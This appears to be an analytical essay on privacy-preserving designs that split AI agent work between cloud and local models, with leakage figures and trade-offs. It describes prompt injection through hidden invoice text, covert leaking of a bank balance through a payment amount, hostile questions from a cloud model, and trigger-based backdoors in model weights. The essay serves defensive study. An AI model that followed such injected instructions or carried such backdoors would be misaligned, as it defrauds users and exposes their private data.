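A local model is probably an easier target than the large closed models that have recently become harder to attack. It is smaller, and an attacker who knows or guesses which open model the user runs can download the same weights, test thousands of versions of an email in private, and send the user only the one that worked.

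The cloud model can also attack through the questions it writes. A hostile question could ask for the most embarrassing fact in the mailbox instead of how much the user owes Kristin. In Radovič and colleagues' design, the program can already read the messages as ordinary text and could copy them without any model's help, but the local model makes a narrow return channel more useful to an attacker. Fifteen bits are of limited use to a program that can only search for keywords, whereas a local model could read ten years of email and report in one bit whether the user is planning to leave their job.

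Relying on the local model to refuse such questions would be unwise. A user might well ask an agent to find evidence of an illness or an affair, and the local model cannot check whether a question came from the user's request or originated with the cloud model.

A careful designer assumes that the local model will obey any text it reads. If the model has no tools, network access or memory, it can only return an answer. If that answer is also wrapped so that only a trusted library function can release it, even a completely manipulated model can't send data out by itself, but it can still return a false answer.

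### An invoice with a false total

Suppose a plumber's invoice for $480 arrives by email. It also contains a line of white text on a white background, which tells automated systems to read the total as $4,800. The user can't see the line, but the local model receives it with the rest of the text. The program asks a reasonable question:

```python
total = slm(
    query="What is the total due on this invoice?",
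    context=invoice_text,
    output_type="float",
)
pay(plumber, total, note="Invoice 118")
```

If the local model follows the hidden line, it returns 4800.0. This is a valid number, so the conversion succeeds and the program pays ten times the bill.

Restricting answers to numbers does prevent another attack, prompt injection. *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025) lets a quarantined model return only whole numbers, decimals, true-or-false values and choices from a fixed list. None of these can contain an instruction, so the planner can safely read them. *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (2026) uses similar types for web-browsing agents and returns free text only if the user approves it.

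Neither method ensures that the answers are true. In one of Jacob and colleagues' examples, a shopping agent receives two scores for each customer review, one for how strongly it supports the product and one for its relevance. A hostile review can't pass the agent an instruction to buy something, but it could cause the quarantined model to give the product ten out of ten. The paper's threat model excludes misleading input. In the split design, misleading input is the problem that matters most for the invoice, because the program pays the total without a planner reading it.

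Fixed rules can check an answer's type, range and permissions, but *Confused ChatGPT* points out that checking its meaning takes another language model. The user's software can still stop a payment without interpreting the invoice.

| Check | Effect on the $4,800 payment |
|---|---|
| The answer must be a number | None |
| The number must appear in the invoice | None, because the hidden line contains it |
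| The local model has no tools or network access | None, because the program makes the payment |
| The program can't pay an amount taken from an email without approval | The broker holds the payment and asks the user |
| The amount must match a quote the user accepted earlier | The broker refuses the payment |
| The user must approve the exact payee and amount | The user can refuse, if they notice the extra zero |

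The fourth check holds the payment because the label on the number records that it came from an email. It doesn't detect whether the number is false, so it would also hold an honest payment of $480. The fifth works only if the user has a quote and the attacker can't change it. For most household bills, the protection depends on a person reading the amount, and they might not notice if a hidden line raised the total to $520.

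An approval also has to specify the exact amount. Dongol analyses an agent that sends replies after the user approves them. If an approval permits any use of the sending tool, an injected instruction can use it to send private data before the approved reply goes out. If it permits only the exact reply, an attacker who sees the messages but not their timing learns nothing extra. A computer has checked the proofs, but they cover only leaks. They exclude attacks that make an agent act wrongly without revealing anything, so they don't rule out an inflated invoice.

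### When a false answer contains a secret

A false answer can also leak data if the program sends it to somebody. Suppose the program gives the local model the user's bank statement along with the invoice, perhaps to check that there is enough money. The hidden line could make the model return the account balance divided by 1,000 as the amount due. If the balance is $4,820, the program pays $4.82, and the plumber can work out the balance from the payment.

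An amount below $1,000 has 100,000 possible values, counting every cent, so a single payment can carry about 16.6 bits (log₂ 100,000). A decimal type doesn't prevent this, and neither does TACIT's wrapper if the library has a payment function that accepts wrapped amounts.

Noninterference is too strict a standard here, since an honest agent's payment also reveals something about the user's data. Dongol proposes comparing the agent with a reference agent that runs the same plan but whose model never obeys untrusted text. In simplified form, let *V*(*d*, *a*) be what the attacker observes when the private data are *d* and the attacker's document is *a*, and let *V*ᵣ be the same for the reference agent. The real agent is secure in this relative sense if, for any two versions *d* and *d*′ of the private data,

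*V*(*d*, *a*) ≠ *V*(*d*′, *a*) for some *a* implies *V*ᵣ(*d*, *a*′) ≠ *V*ᵣ(*d*′, *a*′) for some *a*′.

An attacker is therefore allowed to learn only what some document could have revealed through the task itself. If the reference agent always pays the amount on the invoice, the plumber cannot use any invoice to find out whether the balance is $4,820 or $9,000. The real agent's payment reveals which it is, so the real agent fails the test.

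Dongol treats a corrupted answer as one that can depend on everything the program passed to the model, so the best defence is to pass less. If the local model receives only the invoice, the hidden line can still change the total but can't put the balance into it. The program can check the balance separately with ordinary code. A hostile cloud model wouldn't write its program this carefully, so the user's software has to enforce the separation with labels, for example by refusing to send the plumber a value that came partly from the bank statement.

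### Accurate enough for the question

The local model can also return a false total without any attack. An accuracy of about 95%, the estimate for the 9B model on the harder AppWorld tasks, may be good enough for one question, but small error rates accumulate. If each answer is correct with probability *p* and errors are independent, the probability that all *n* answers are correct is

*p*ⁿ.

If the local model answers each question correctly 95% of the time and its errors are independent, it has a 77% chance of answering five questions without an error and a 36% chance of answering twenty. Real errors probably cluster in difficult documents, so these figures are only a rough guide.

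Searching a mailbox can produce even worse results. Suppose 10 of 1,000 emails are bills from a clinic, and the local model correctly classifies 95% of the bills and 95% of the other emails. It will find 9 or 10 of the bills but also mislabel about 50 of the other 990 emails as bills. Only about one in six of the emails it selects will be a bill, so a program that adds up the amounts will produce a meaningless total. The program should first use ordinary code to narrow the search, for example by selecting emails from the clinic's address.

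Ordinary code can also catch some wrong answers. It can check that the items on an invoice add up to the total, or that a number the model returns appears somewhere in the document. The second check would catch an invented number, but not a wrong number taken from the document. A second local model, preferably from a different developer, could also answer the same question, and the program could stop if the two answers disagree.

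How accurate the model needs to be depends on what the program does with its output. If the model mislabels a newsletter, the user can move it back. Payments and medical letters need approval before they are sent, even if the model is right 99% of the time, because the user may not be able to undo a wrong payment or a letter sent to the wrong person.

### Where the weights come from

The user also has to trust the local model's developer. This became a public question in September 2026, when Perplexity released an agent that handles confidential work with a model on the user's Mac. Nuñez (2026), in *Your files stay put*, reports that two of the three available models were versions of Qwen, from the Chinese company Alibaba. The third was Google's Gemma.

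VentureBeat asked whether business or government customers had objected to running a Chinese model on their machines. Jon Staff, who leads Perplexity's Mac and iPhone engineering, replied that the company could evaluate the models itself because their weights were open. He added that data doesn't leave the computer when the model runs locally and that macOS's sandbox limits what the agent can do.

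Staff is right that offline weights can't send data to Alibaba. Weights are numbers, so any network connection must come from the software around them. Ibrahim and colleagues monitored 205 Ollama runs and saw no attempts to contact an outside server. They found the same with LM Studio. The models they tested included a version of Qwen.

The file that contains the weights deserves more suspicion than the weights themselves. It also holds settings and a template for formatting prompts, and a flaw recorded in 2026 in another serving system, SGLang, let a malicious template run code on the server. Ibrahim and colleagues tested llama.cpp's file reader more than 12 million times over 24 hours without causing a crash, but they also list several earlier memory flaws in it. If the model runs in a sandbox without network access, Staff's claim still holds even if a file exploits a new flaw.

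His reply doesn't address what the model does with the data while it is on the machine. A developer could train a backdoor into a model, so that it behaves normally except when a particular phrase or name appears. The model might read invoices correctly for years but return a different account number whenever a certain supplier's name occurs. It wouldn't need a network connection, because the program would make the payment. Nuñez reports a concern about Qwen's origin but no evidence that Qwen behaves this way.

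Open weights make testing easier, but testing is a weak defence against a backdoor. If a company tests the model on 10,000 randomly chosen invoices and finds no errors, it can be 95% confident that the error rate on similar invoices is below about 0.03%. But it learns almost nothing about how the model handles an invoice containing the trigger, since whoever chose the trigger would have picked something testers were unlikely to try. Reading the weights doesn't help much either, because people can't predict what a model will do from billions of numbers the way they often can from source code. The checks on the invoice payment are more useful because they work whether the false number comes from a hidden line, a backdoor or an ordinary mistake.

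Biased answers are harder to catch. Suppose a company asks its agent to summarise reports about its suppliers, and the local model's developer trained it to avoid politically sensitive subjects such as forced labour. The summary may leave out the most important paragraph, and the user won't notice without reading the reports. The broker won't ask for approval, because the summary involves no payment or other action. A question with a narrow factual answer, such as an invoice total, leaves less room for bias than a summary does. For sensitive subjects, the company could compare summaries from models by different developers, or at least read some of the originals.

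These concerns apply to any developer, and a model may pass through several hands. Perplexity recommends a version of Qwen that it has trained further. Ibrahim and colleagues got all four of their models as compressed files from a community group on Hugging Face rather than from the original developers. They recorded a digest of each file, but a digest can't show whether somebody had tampered with the model before then.

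The same developer may supply both models. In the AppWorld experiment, the cloud and local models were both Qwen models. That was reasonable for measuring performance, but a user who treats the cloud model's developer as a possible attacker would be giving the private data to another of that developer's models. TACIT's wrapper would still prevent the local model from sending the data out by itself, but the user would have little reason to believe the local model's summaries.

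## Designs that send the cloud model a filtered view of the data

When a code-first agent works as intended, its cloud model receives nothing from the clinic's letter. This protects the user but leaves the stronger model with little to reason about. Other designs send the cloud model something derived from the private data, such as a few extracts, a reworded request, text with names replaced by labels, or an outline of which files exist. In these designs, the user's side has to decide what to let through.

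### Extracts chosen for relevance

*Minions* (Narayan, Biderman and colleagues, 2025) describes the design most similar to the code-first split. A user asks a question about a long document, such as a company's annual report. Without reading the document, the cloud model writes a Python function that cuts the text into chunks and pairs each chunk with a simple instruction, for example to extract the total revenue for 2015. Fewer than fifteen lines of code can create hundreds of these small jobs.

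The local model runs the jobs in parallel. For each one, it either abstains or returns an answer with an explanation and a citation. Software on the user's machine discards the abstentions and sends the rest to the cloud model, which answers the question or writes another round of jobs. The grocery task differs mainly in that its program used the amount Kristin was owed without sending it to the cloud.

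The design works well for its purpose of saving money. On three sets of questions about financial, medical and scientific documents, an 8B local model working with GPT-4o answered 70.9% correctly. GPT-4o scored 72.4% when it read the documents itself, and the local model scored 44.4% alone. The average cloud cost per question fell from $0.233 to $0.042. At GPT-4o's price of $2.50 per million input tokens, $0.233 pays for about 93,000 tokens and $0.042 for at most 16,800, so the user's machine uploaded far less text.

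A simpler version let the two models chat freely while only the local one had the document. It cost less than a cent per question but scored 63.0%, and on the scientific papers it did worse than the local model alone. Separate tests suggest that the local model handled multi-part instructions and long texts poorly. Splitting such instructions into separate requests raised a 3B model's score by 56 points, and lengthening the text from under 1,000 tokens to over 65,000 lowered its score by 13%. These results also support Radovič and colleagues' recommendation to use narrow, single questions with `slm`.

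Narayan and colleagues say that they don't address privacy, and they give no leakage figures. Their filter may work against privacy, because it keeps only what is relevant to the question. If a user asks whether her medical records suggest a relapse, the extracts will be the passages about a relapse. Her machine might reveal nearly everything she wanted to hide while uploading only a twentieth of the records.

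### Rewriting the request

The weakness of the code-first split is that the cloud model receives the request as the user typed it. *PAPILLON* (Li, Raghuram and colleagues, 2024) has a local model write a new request without the personal details, then combine the cloud model's answer with the original request. In one example, a user wants a formal email about a job he has applied for at WIPRO in Noida. The cloud model receives a request for a formal email to the human resources department of "a company".

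Li and colleagues tested this on 237 prompts that people had sent to ChatGPT, with about three private items in each. With Llama 3.1 8B as the local model and GPT-4o-mini in the cloud, a judge model rated 85.5% of the answers at least as good as ChatGPT's originals, and 7.5% of the private items remained in the rewritten prompts. With the five other local models, between 11.9% and 39.3% remained.

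The cloud model contributed little to that result. Llama scored 81.5% when it answered the original prompts on its own, so sending rewritten prompts to the cloud improved about ten answers out of 237. Human raters agreed with the judge on only 65% to 71% of the pairs they checked, which makes such a small difference hard to trust. For everyday writing tasks like these, a user with an 8B model might choose to use only the local model. Rewriting is more useful when the local model can't do the task, but harder tasks also tend to depend on details that the rewriting removes. Some rewritten prompts lost the point of the request altogether, such as a request to rewrite an email that became a question about cheap transport.

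Rewriting did much worse with agents that use tools. In tests by *PAAC*, an adapted version of the method left more than 85% of the private items in the text sent to the cloud. Those tests may understate what the method can do, because a rival team ran them and used a 4B local model instead of an 8B one. There is still good reason to expect trouble, because an agent needs the exact order number to look up an order, so the local model must either leave the number in the prompt or break the tool call.

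### Placeholders for private values

*PAAC* solves the order number problem with placeholders. A local model reads the request and proposes which words to hide, following a checklist the user can edit. Ordinary software replaces each one with a typed label such as ORDER_ID_1 and keeps the real values in a table on the device. When the cloud model requests a tool call with that label, the software puts the real number back and makes the call. The local model then condenses the result into short findings, and the software masks those too before sending them to the cloud model.

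The cloud model can therefore work in a loop and change its plan after each step, which a code-first agent's cloud model can do only after a crash. It also has to leave calculations to the device. Suppose Alice has $1,234 in the bank and pays $1,000 in rent. Some privacy systems disguise such values by adding noise, so the cloud model might receive $1,500 and $980, subtract them and answer $520. If it receives only the placeholders BALANCE and RENT, it has to request the calculation from the device, which returns the correct $234.

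The tests used Gemini 3 Flash as the cloud model and Qwen3-4B as the local one. They covered τ²-bench's airline and retail tasks and 20 tasks from GAIA, a benchmark of open-ended assistant tasks. The baseline was Gemini working alone behind conventional masking software, which uses fixed patterns to recognise names, numbers and other standard categories. The table gives *PAAC*'s results with an ordinary reading loop.

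| Tasks | Agent | Completed without masking (%) | Completed under the strictest policy (%) | Private items left in under the strictest policy (%) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Airline | Gemini with pattern-based masking | 88.7 | 66.7 | 49.9 |
| Airline | *PAAC* | 84.7 | 64.0 | 15.7 |
| Retail | Gemini with pattern-based masking | 59.6 | 28.4 | 51.5 |
| Retail | *PAAC* | 89.8 | 58.5 | 16.2 |
| GAIA | Gemini with pattern-based masking | 48.3 | 23.3 | 15.1 |
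| GAIA | *PAAC* | 58.3 | 31.7 | 20.0 |

On the customer-service tasks, the placeholders left in about a third as many private items as the patterns did. On GAIA they left in slightly more, but 20 tasks are too few to show which method leaves in fewer. Hiding the values lowered *PAAC*'s completion rate in every case, by 21 to 31 points between no masking and the strictest policy. *PAAC* already had its large lead on the retail tasks without masking, so the lead must come from dividing the work between the models and not from the placeholders.

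The leakage figures also omit private values that first appeared in a tool's result, such as an address in a customer's record. Three evaluator models listed the private items in each user's request, and software then searched only for those items in the text sent to the cloud. The figures also exclude the labels, which the design reveals on purpose. The provider can infer from a label such as ONCOLOGIST_1 that the user probably has cancer, even though the label hides the doctor's name.

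The placeholders protected private values well against hidden instructions. When the researchers planted text in tool results telling the local model to reveal private values, the attack caused at most 0.2% of those values to reach the cloud. One attack imitated the wording of the local model's own prompts. In puzzles about family relationships, it got past the model's first check about 84% of the time, but the masking step still hid the names. Entries in the table of real values can be added but never removed, so a manipulated model can't make the software unmask a value from the original request.

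### What a detector misses

Every masking system has to find a private item before it can hide it. *PAAC* states the consequence as a theorem. Let *S* be the set of private items in a text and *r* the recall, meaning the share of all private items that the detector finds. Then the expected number of items that leak satisfies

E[leaked items] ≥ (1 − *r*) · E[|*S*|].

The bound holds no matter how well the software protects the private items it finds, because it passes the items it misses through unchanged. If a detector finds 90% of the private items, at least 10% will leak, even if the software perfectly encrypts the ones it finds.

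In an experiment with the family puzzles, the researchers kept the same pattern-based detector and varied how they obscured the names it found. Plain masking left 39.4% of the names in the text, and random noise at five different strengths left between 40.4% and 41.2%. When a local language model did the detecting, no names remained. But language models aren't always better detectors. On general-knowledge questions where the policy covered ordinary nouns, the local model missed 42.0% of those nouns, while the patterns missed only 6.3%.

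The most sensitive items can be the hardest to detect. On a collection of 1,000 texts with labelled personal data, *PAAC* let through 9.7% of private items overall but 23.4% of credentials. Detection rules written by three frontier models, applied together, let through 13.3% overall and 63.0% of credentials. Passwords are hard to detect because, unlike email addresses, they need not follow a recognisable format.

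In *LLM-Redactor*, Agyemang, Kponyo and colleagues (2026) measured how much private data remains after redaction, using 1,300 synthetic prompts with 4,014 labelled private items. Their best practical combination of methods starts with a 3B local model, which answers the prompts it judges to be simple. For the remaining prompts, software masks the private items it detects, and a local model rephrases the text before it goes to the cloud. The combination leaked 0.6% of the private items in ordinary prose about people. The table shows where that figure comes from.

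| Type of prompt | Leaked with masking alone (%) | Answered locally (%) | Leaked with the full combination (%) | Leaked among items in prompts sent to the cloud (%) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Personal details | 15.3 | 94.4 | 0.6 | About 10 |
| Passwords and keys | 31.8 | 74.7 | 6.4 | About 26 |
| Identity implied by context | 95.0 | 54.0 | 43.6 | About 93 |
| Company code | 58.5 | 38.0 | 31.3 | About 52 |

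The last column divides the combination's leak rate by the rate for local answering alone, which leaves any prompt sent to the cloud unaltered. The combination's leak rate is only 0.6% mostly because 472 of the 500 prompts were answered on the device. When a prompt went to the cloud, roughly one private item in ten still leaked. Agyemang and colleagues didn't test whether the 3B model answered the prompts kept on the device well.

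An item counts as leaked in these rates if any four consecutive characters of it survive, so the rates overstate the harm in some cases. No complete name, address or other personal detail got through in the first group. But 12.3% of the private items in company code got through whole, even with every step switched on.

The standard detector missed 79.8% of employee numbers, but adding one rule that described their format cut the miss rate to zero. An organisation can write similar rules for its own identifiers if it knows which ones it uses. Redaction made the answers worse. In a small test, a judge model rated the answer to the original prompt above the answer to the redacted one in 75% to 80% of cases.

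### Identifying someone from harmless details

A text can identify a person without containing anything a detector would flag. One of Agyemang and colleagues' examples is a chief financial officer whose wife works at a competitor. If the software removes the company's name and the local model rewrites the rest as "a senior executive whose spouse works at a competitor", someone who knows the industry may still recognise the couple.

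A judge model classified at least 95% of such texts as still identifying the person, whether the software had masked them, rephrased them or left them unchanged. The test used only 20 texts, and the judge had the right answer in advance, which made recognition easier than it would be for a stranger. The problem is still real, because users often ask about the relationship itself, so it can't be removed without losing the question.

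Harmless details become identifying when they occur together. In this constructed example, one person in 50 in a city of a million is a teacher, one in 100 has twins, and one in 200 had a hip operation this year. If the three facts are independent, the expected number of people who fit all of them is

1,000,000 × 1/50 × 1/100 × 1/200 = 1.

A detector that judges each detail separately has no reason to hide any of the three.

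*PlanTwin* sends the cloud model descriptions of the user's files, but none of their text. Software on the user's side turns each file into a record with fixed fields, such as its kind, its role, how recent and sensitive it is, and what it contains. A record might describe a recent, restricted requirements document with tables and dates. The cloud model receives these records and the links between them, and plans by choosing from a fixed list of operations, such as auditing one file or comparing two. A local gatekeeper checks each operation and runs it on the real files.

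None of the passwords, names or other sensitive items in 60 synthetic tasks reached the four cloud models tested, because the format has no field that can hold free text. Simple pattern-based redaction let through 16.5% of the same items overall, and 88% of those in the coding tasks.

On a scale from 0 to 1, Kimi K2.5's planning score fell from 0.843 with the full data to 0.808 with the records, while Gemini 3 Flash's fell further, from 0.832 to 0.689. The score measures whether the model chose the expected operations, not whether those operations were enough to finish the task. The paper's headline loss of under 2.2% is smaller because it compares versions of the system with one another, not with a planner that has the full data.

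To test how well the records identify files, the researchers gave an attacker one record and 15 candidate files. Random guessing found the right file 6.6% of the time. The attacker found it in 33.5% of trials when using only the kind of file, 78.6% when also using the role, and 94.1% when using all the fields. With 30 candidates, the attacker still found the right file more than 88% of the time using all the fields.

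A theorem in *PlanTwin* explains what protection would require. Suppose that *k* files fit the fields the cloud model has received, and that all of them are equally likely before the attacker uses any outside knowledge. If that knowledge favours one of these files over another by at most a factor of η, the attacker identifies the right one with probability at most

η / (η + *k* − 1).

With 15 matching files and no outside knowledge (η = 1), the bound is 1/15. If outside knowledge can favour a file by a factor of five, the bound rises to 5/19, or about 26%. If only one file fits the fields, the bound is 1, so it gives no protection.

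The gatekeeper therefore limits how many fields it releases about each file. Each field has a weight, such as 0.5 for the kind of file, 2 for its role and 3 for each link to another file. The weights in the requirements document's record would add up to about 8. Once the fields released about a file reach its limit, the gatekeeper withholds the rest. The attack ran without these limits, so it shows why they are needed but doesn't measure how well they work. The limits can also make the cloud model useless. When they were set to a quarter of their normal size, the planning score fell to 0.513, below the 0.567 that a 1B local model achieved without a cloud model.

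### Asking the user about flagged content

Perplexity sells a design of this general kind as Hybrid Compute, the September 2026 Mac product whose Chinese local models prompted VentureBeat's question. Perplexity says that a cloud model directs the task and hands private work to a second agent on the user's machine. A classifier on the machine checks content before it goes to the cloud, and the software asks the user before sending anything the classifier flags.

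Unlike the model in the code-first split, Perplexity's cloud model can by default receive text from the user's files as the task proceeds and use it to choose the next step. It should therefore handle surprises better than a model that has to write the whole program in advance, but the user has to rely on the classifier. The company's assurance that data stay on the computer when the model runs locally applies to the work that the local agent keeps, not to what the local side sends to the cloud model.

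Even a good classifier can let private text through. Suppose it recognises 95% of private passages, and 40 such passages reach the boundary during a long task. If its errors are independent, the chance that it misses at least one is 1 − 0.95⁴⁰, or about 87%. The user isn't asked about missed passages. They are asked about the other 38 or so, and people tend to approve such requests without reading them. A stricter classifier would miss fewer passages but lead to more requests.

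Perplexity's classifier may be much better or worse than this. The company's description explains the design but doesn't include measured performance, and a buyer would need to know the miss rate on documents like their own.

### Protecting marked data or withholding everything

All these designs need some way to tell private data from other data. They differ in what happens to a private detail that no person or software has recognised as private.

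| Design | What the cloud model receives | What decides | What happens to an unrecognised private detail |
|---|---|---|---|
| Narayan and colleagues | Extracts, explanations and citations | Local model, by relevance | It goes up if it bears on the question |
| Li and colleagues | A rewritten request | Local model | It may remain in the new request |
| *PAAC* | Text with placeholders | Local model, under the user's policy | It goes up unchanged |
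| *PlanTwin* | Records with fixed fields | A fixed format and a disclosure limit | Its text stays, but the record may hint at it |
| Hybrid Compute | Content that passes the check | Classifier, then the user if it flags something | It goes up without a question |
| Code-first split | Request, documentation, error traces | The user's software, by default | It stays, unless it is in the request or an error trace |

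Like language models that search for names, TACIT depends on the labelling assumption, since it wraps only the contents of folders marked as classified.

Marking data correctly is difficult because privacy depends on context. The name of a user's city is harmless in a question about the weather, but it may identify her in a question about a rare disease. *PAAC* lets users add their own categories to its checklist, but few people could list in advance everything they would object to sharing. *PAAC* argues that a system should hide too much rather than too little, since the user can recover from a failed task but can't take back a disclosure.

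Hiding more data limits how much the cloud model can help. If it receives CITY_1 instead of Lisbon and has no map or search tool, it can't use what it knows about Lisbon to suggest a museum. *PAAC* acknowledges this limitation. At the extreme, the code-first split withholds every file by default, which is partly why it completed fewer AppWorld tasks than the reading loop.

Withholding data by default seems the better starting point for a mailbox, because nobody can list its private details in advance. The user can then release particular facts when a task needs them. The private fields in a company's order system have known names and formats, so replacing them with placeholders should miss fewer private details, and the cloud model can keep working in a loop.

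These designs can also be combined. A code-first agent could withhold all the files and use a local model to rewrite only the request, which is the one part always sent to the cloud model. Any private detail the rewrite missed would then come from the sentence or two the user typed rather than from ten years of email.

### Confidential computing

A different approach sends the cloud model the original text and tries to prevent the provider from reading it. Confidential computing runs the model in a trusted execution environment, or enclave, which the hardware isolates from the rest of the machine so that the machine's operator can't ordinarily look inside. The user's software first requests an attestation, a hardware-signed measurement of the enclave's code and settings, and sends the private data only if the measurement matches the expected one.

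A model running in an enclave reads everything, so it loses nothing to masking or abstraction. The leak rate is 100% by Agyemang and colleagues' measure, which counts private items in the transmitted text regardless of who can read them on arrival. They recommend enclaves for cases such as the financial officer and his wife, where no rewording can hide the person and preserve the question. They list Apple's Private Cloud Compute, Microsoft's Azure and Nvidia's H100 processors among the most mature options. They tested only attestation checks for Amazon's Nitro Enclaves, which added less than 100 milliseconds. They didn't run a language model in an enclave, so the study provides no evidence about how fast or reliable that would be.

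With an enclave, the customer trusts the company that makes the hardware and signs the measurements, rather than the provider's staff and retention policy. Agyemang and colleagues warn that enclaves don't protect against a compromised manufacturer, or against side channels in the hardware that reveal data indirectly. The hardware company may also run the data centres. Amazon designs the Nitro system and runs the data centres that use it, so a customer who distrusts Amazon gains little from Amazon's signature.

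The user also has to trust whoever has examined the code. An attestation identifies the program that is running but doesn't show that the program keeps data private. A program could write prompts to a log outside the enclave and still pass attestation. One local application logged prompts by default, though to users' own disks. Outsiders can check for such logging only if the provider publishes the code and lets them reproduce the measurement.

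An enclave does not make the model trustworthy either. A model in an enclave can still follow instructions hidden in an email, so it needs the same limits on tools and network access as a local model. *PlanTwin* argues that hardware protection does not settle how much data the model should receive.

An enclave with those limits would resemble the user's own hardware, except that it is rented. A user who trusted it could run the whole reading loop there and avoid the split agent's lower scores. But a flaw in the enclave could expose every email the model had read, rather than the single name that a missed placeholder exposes.
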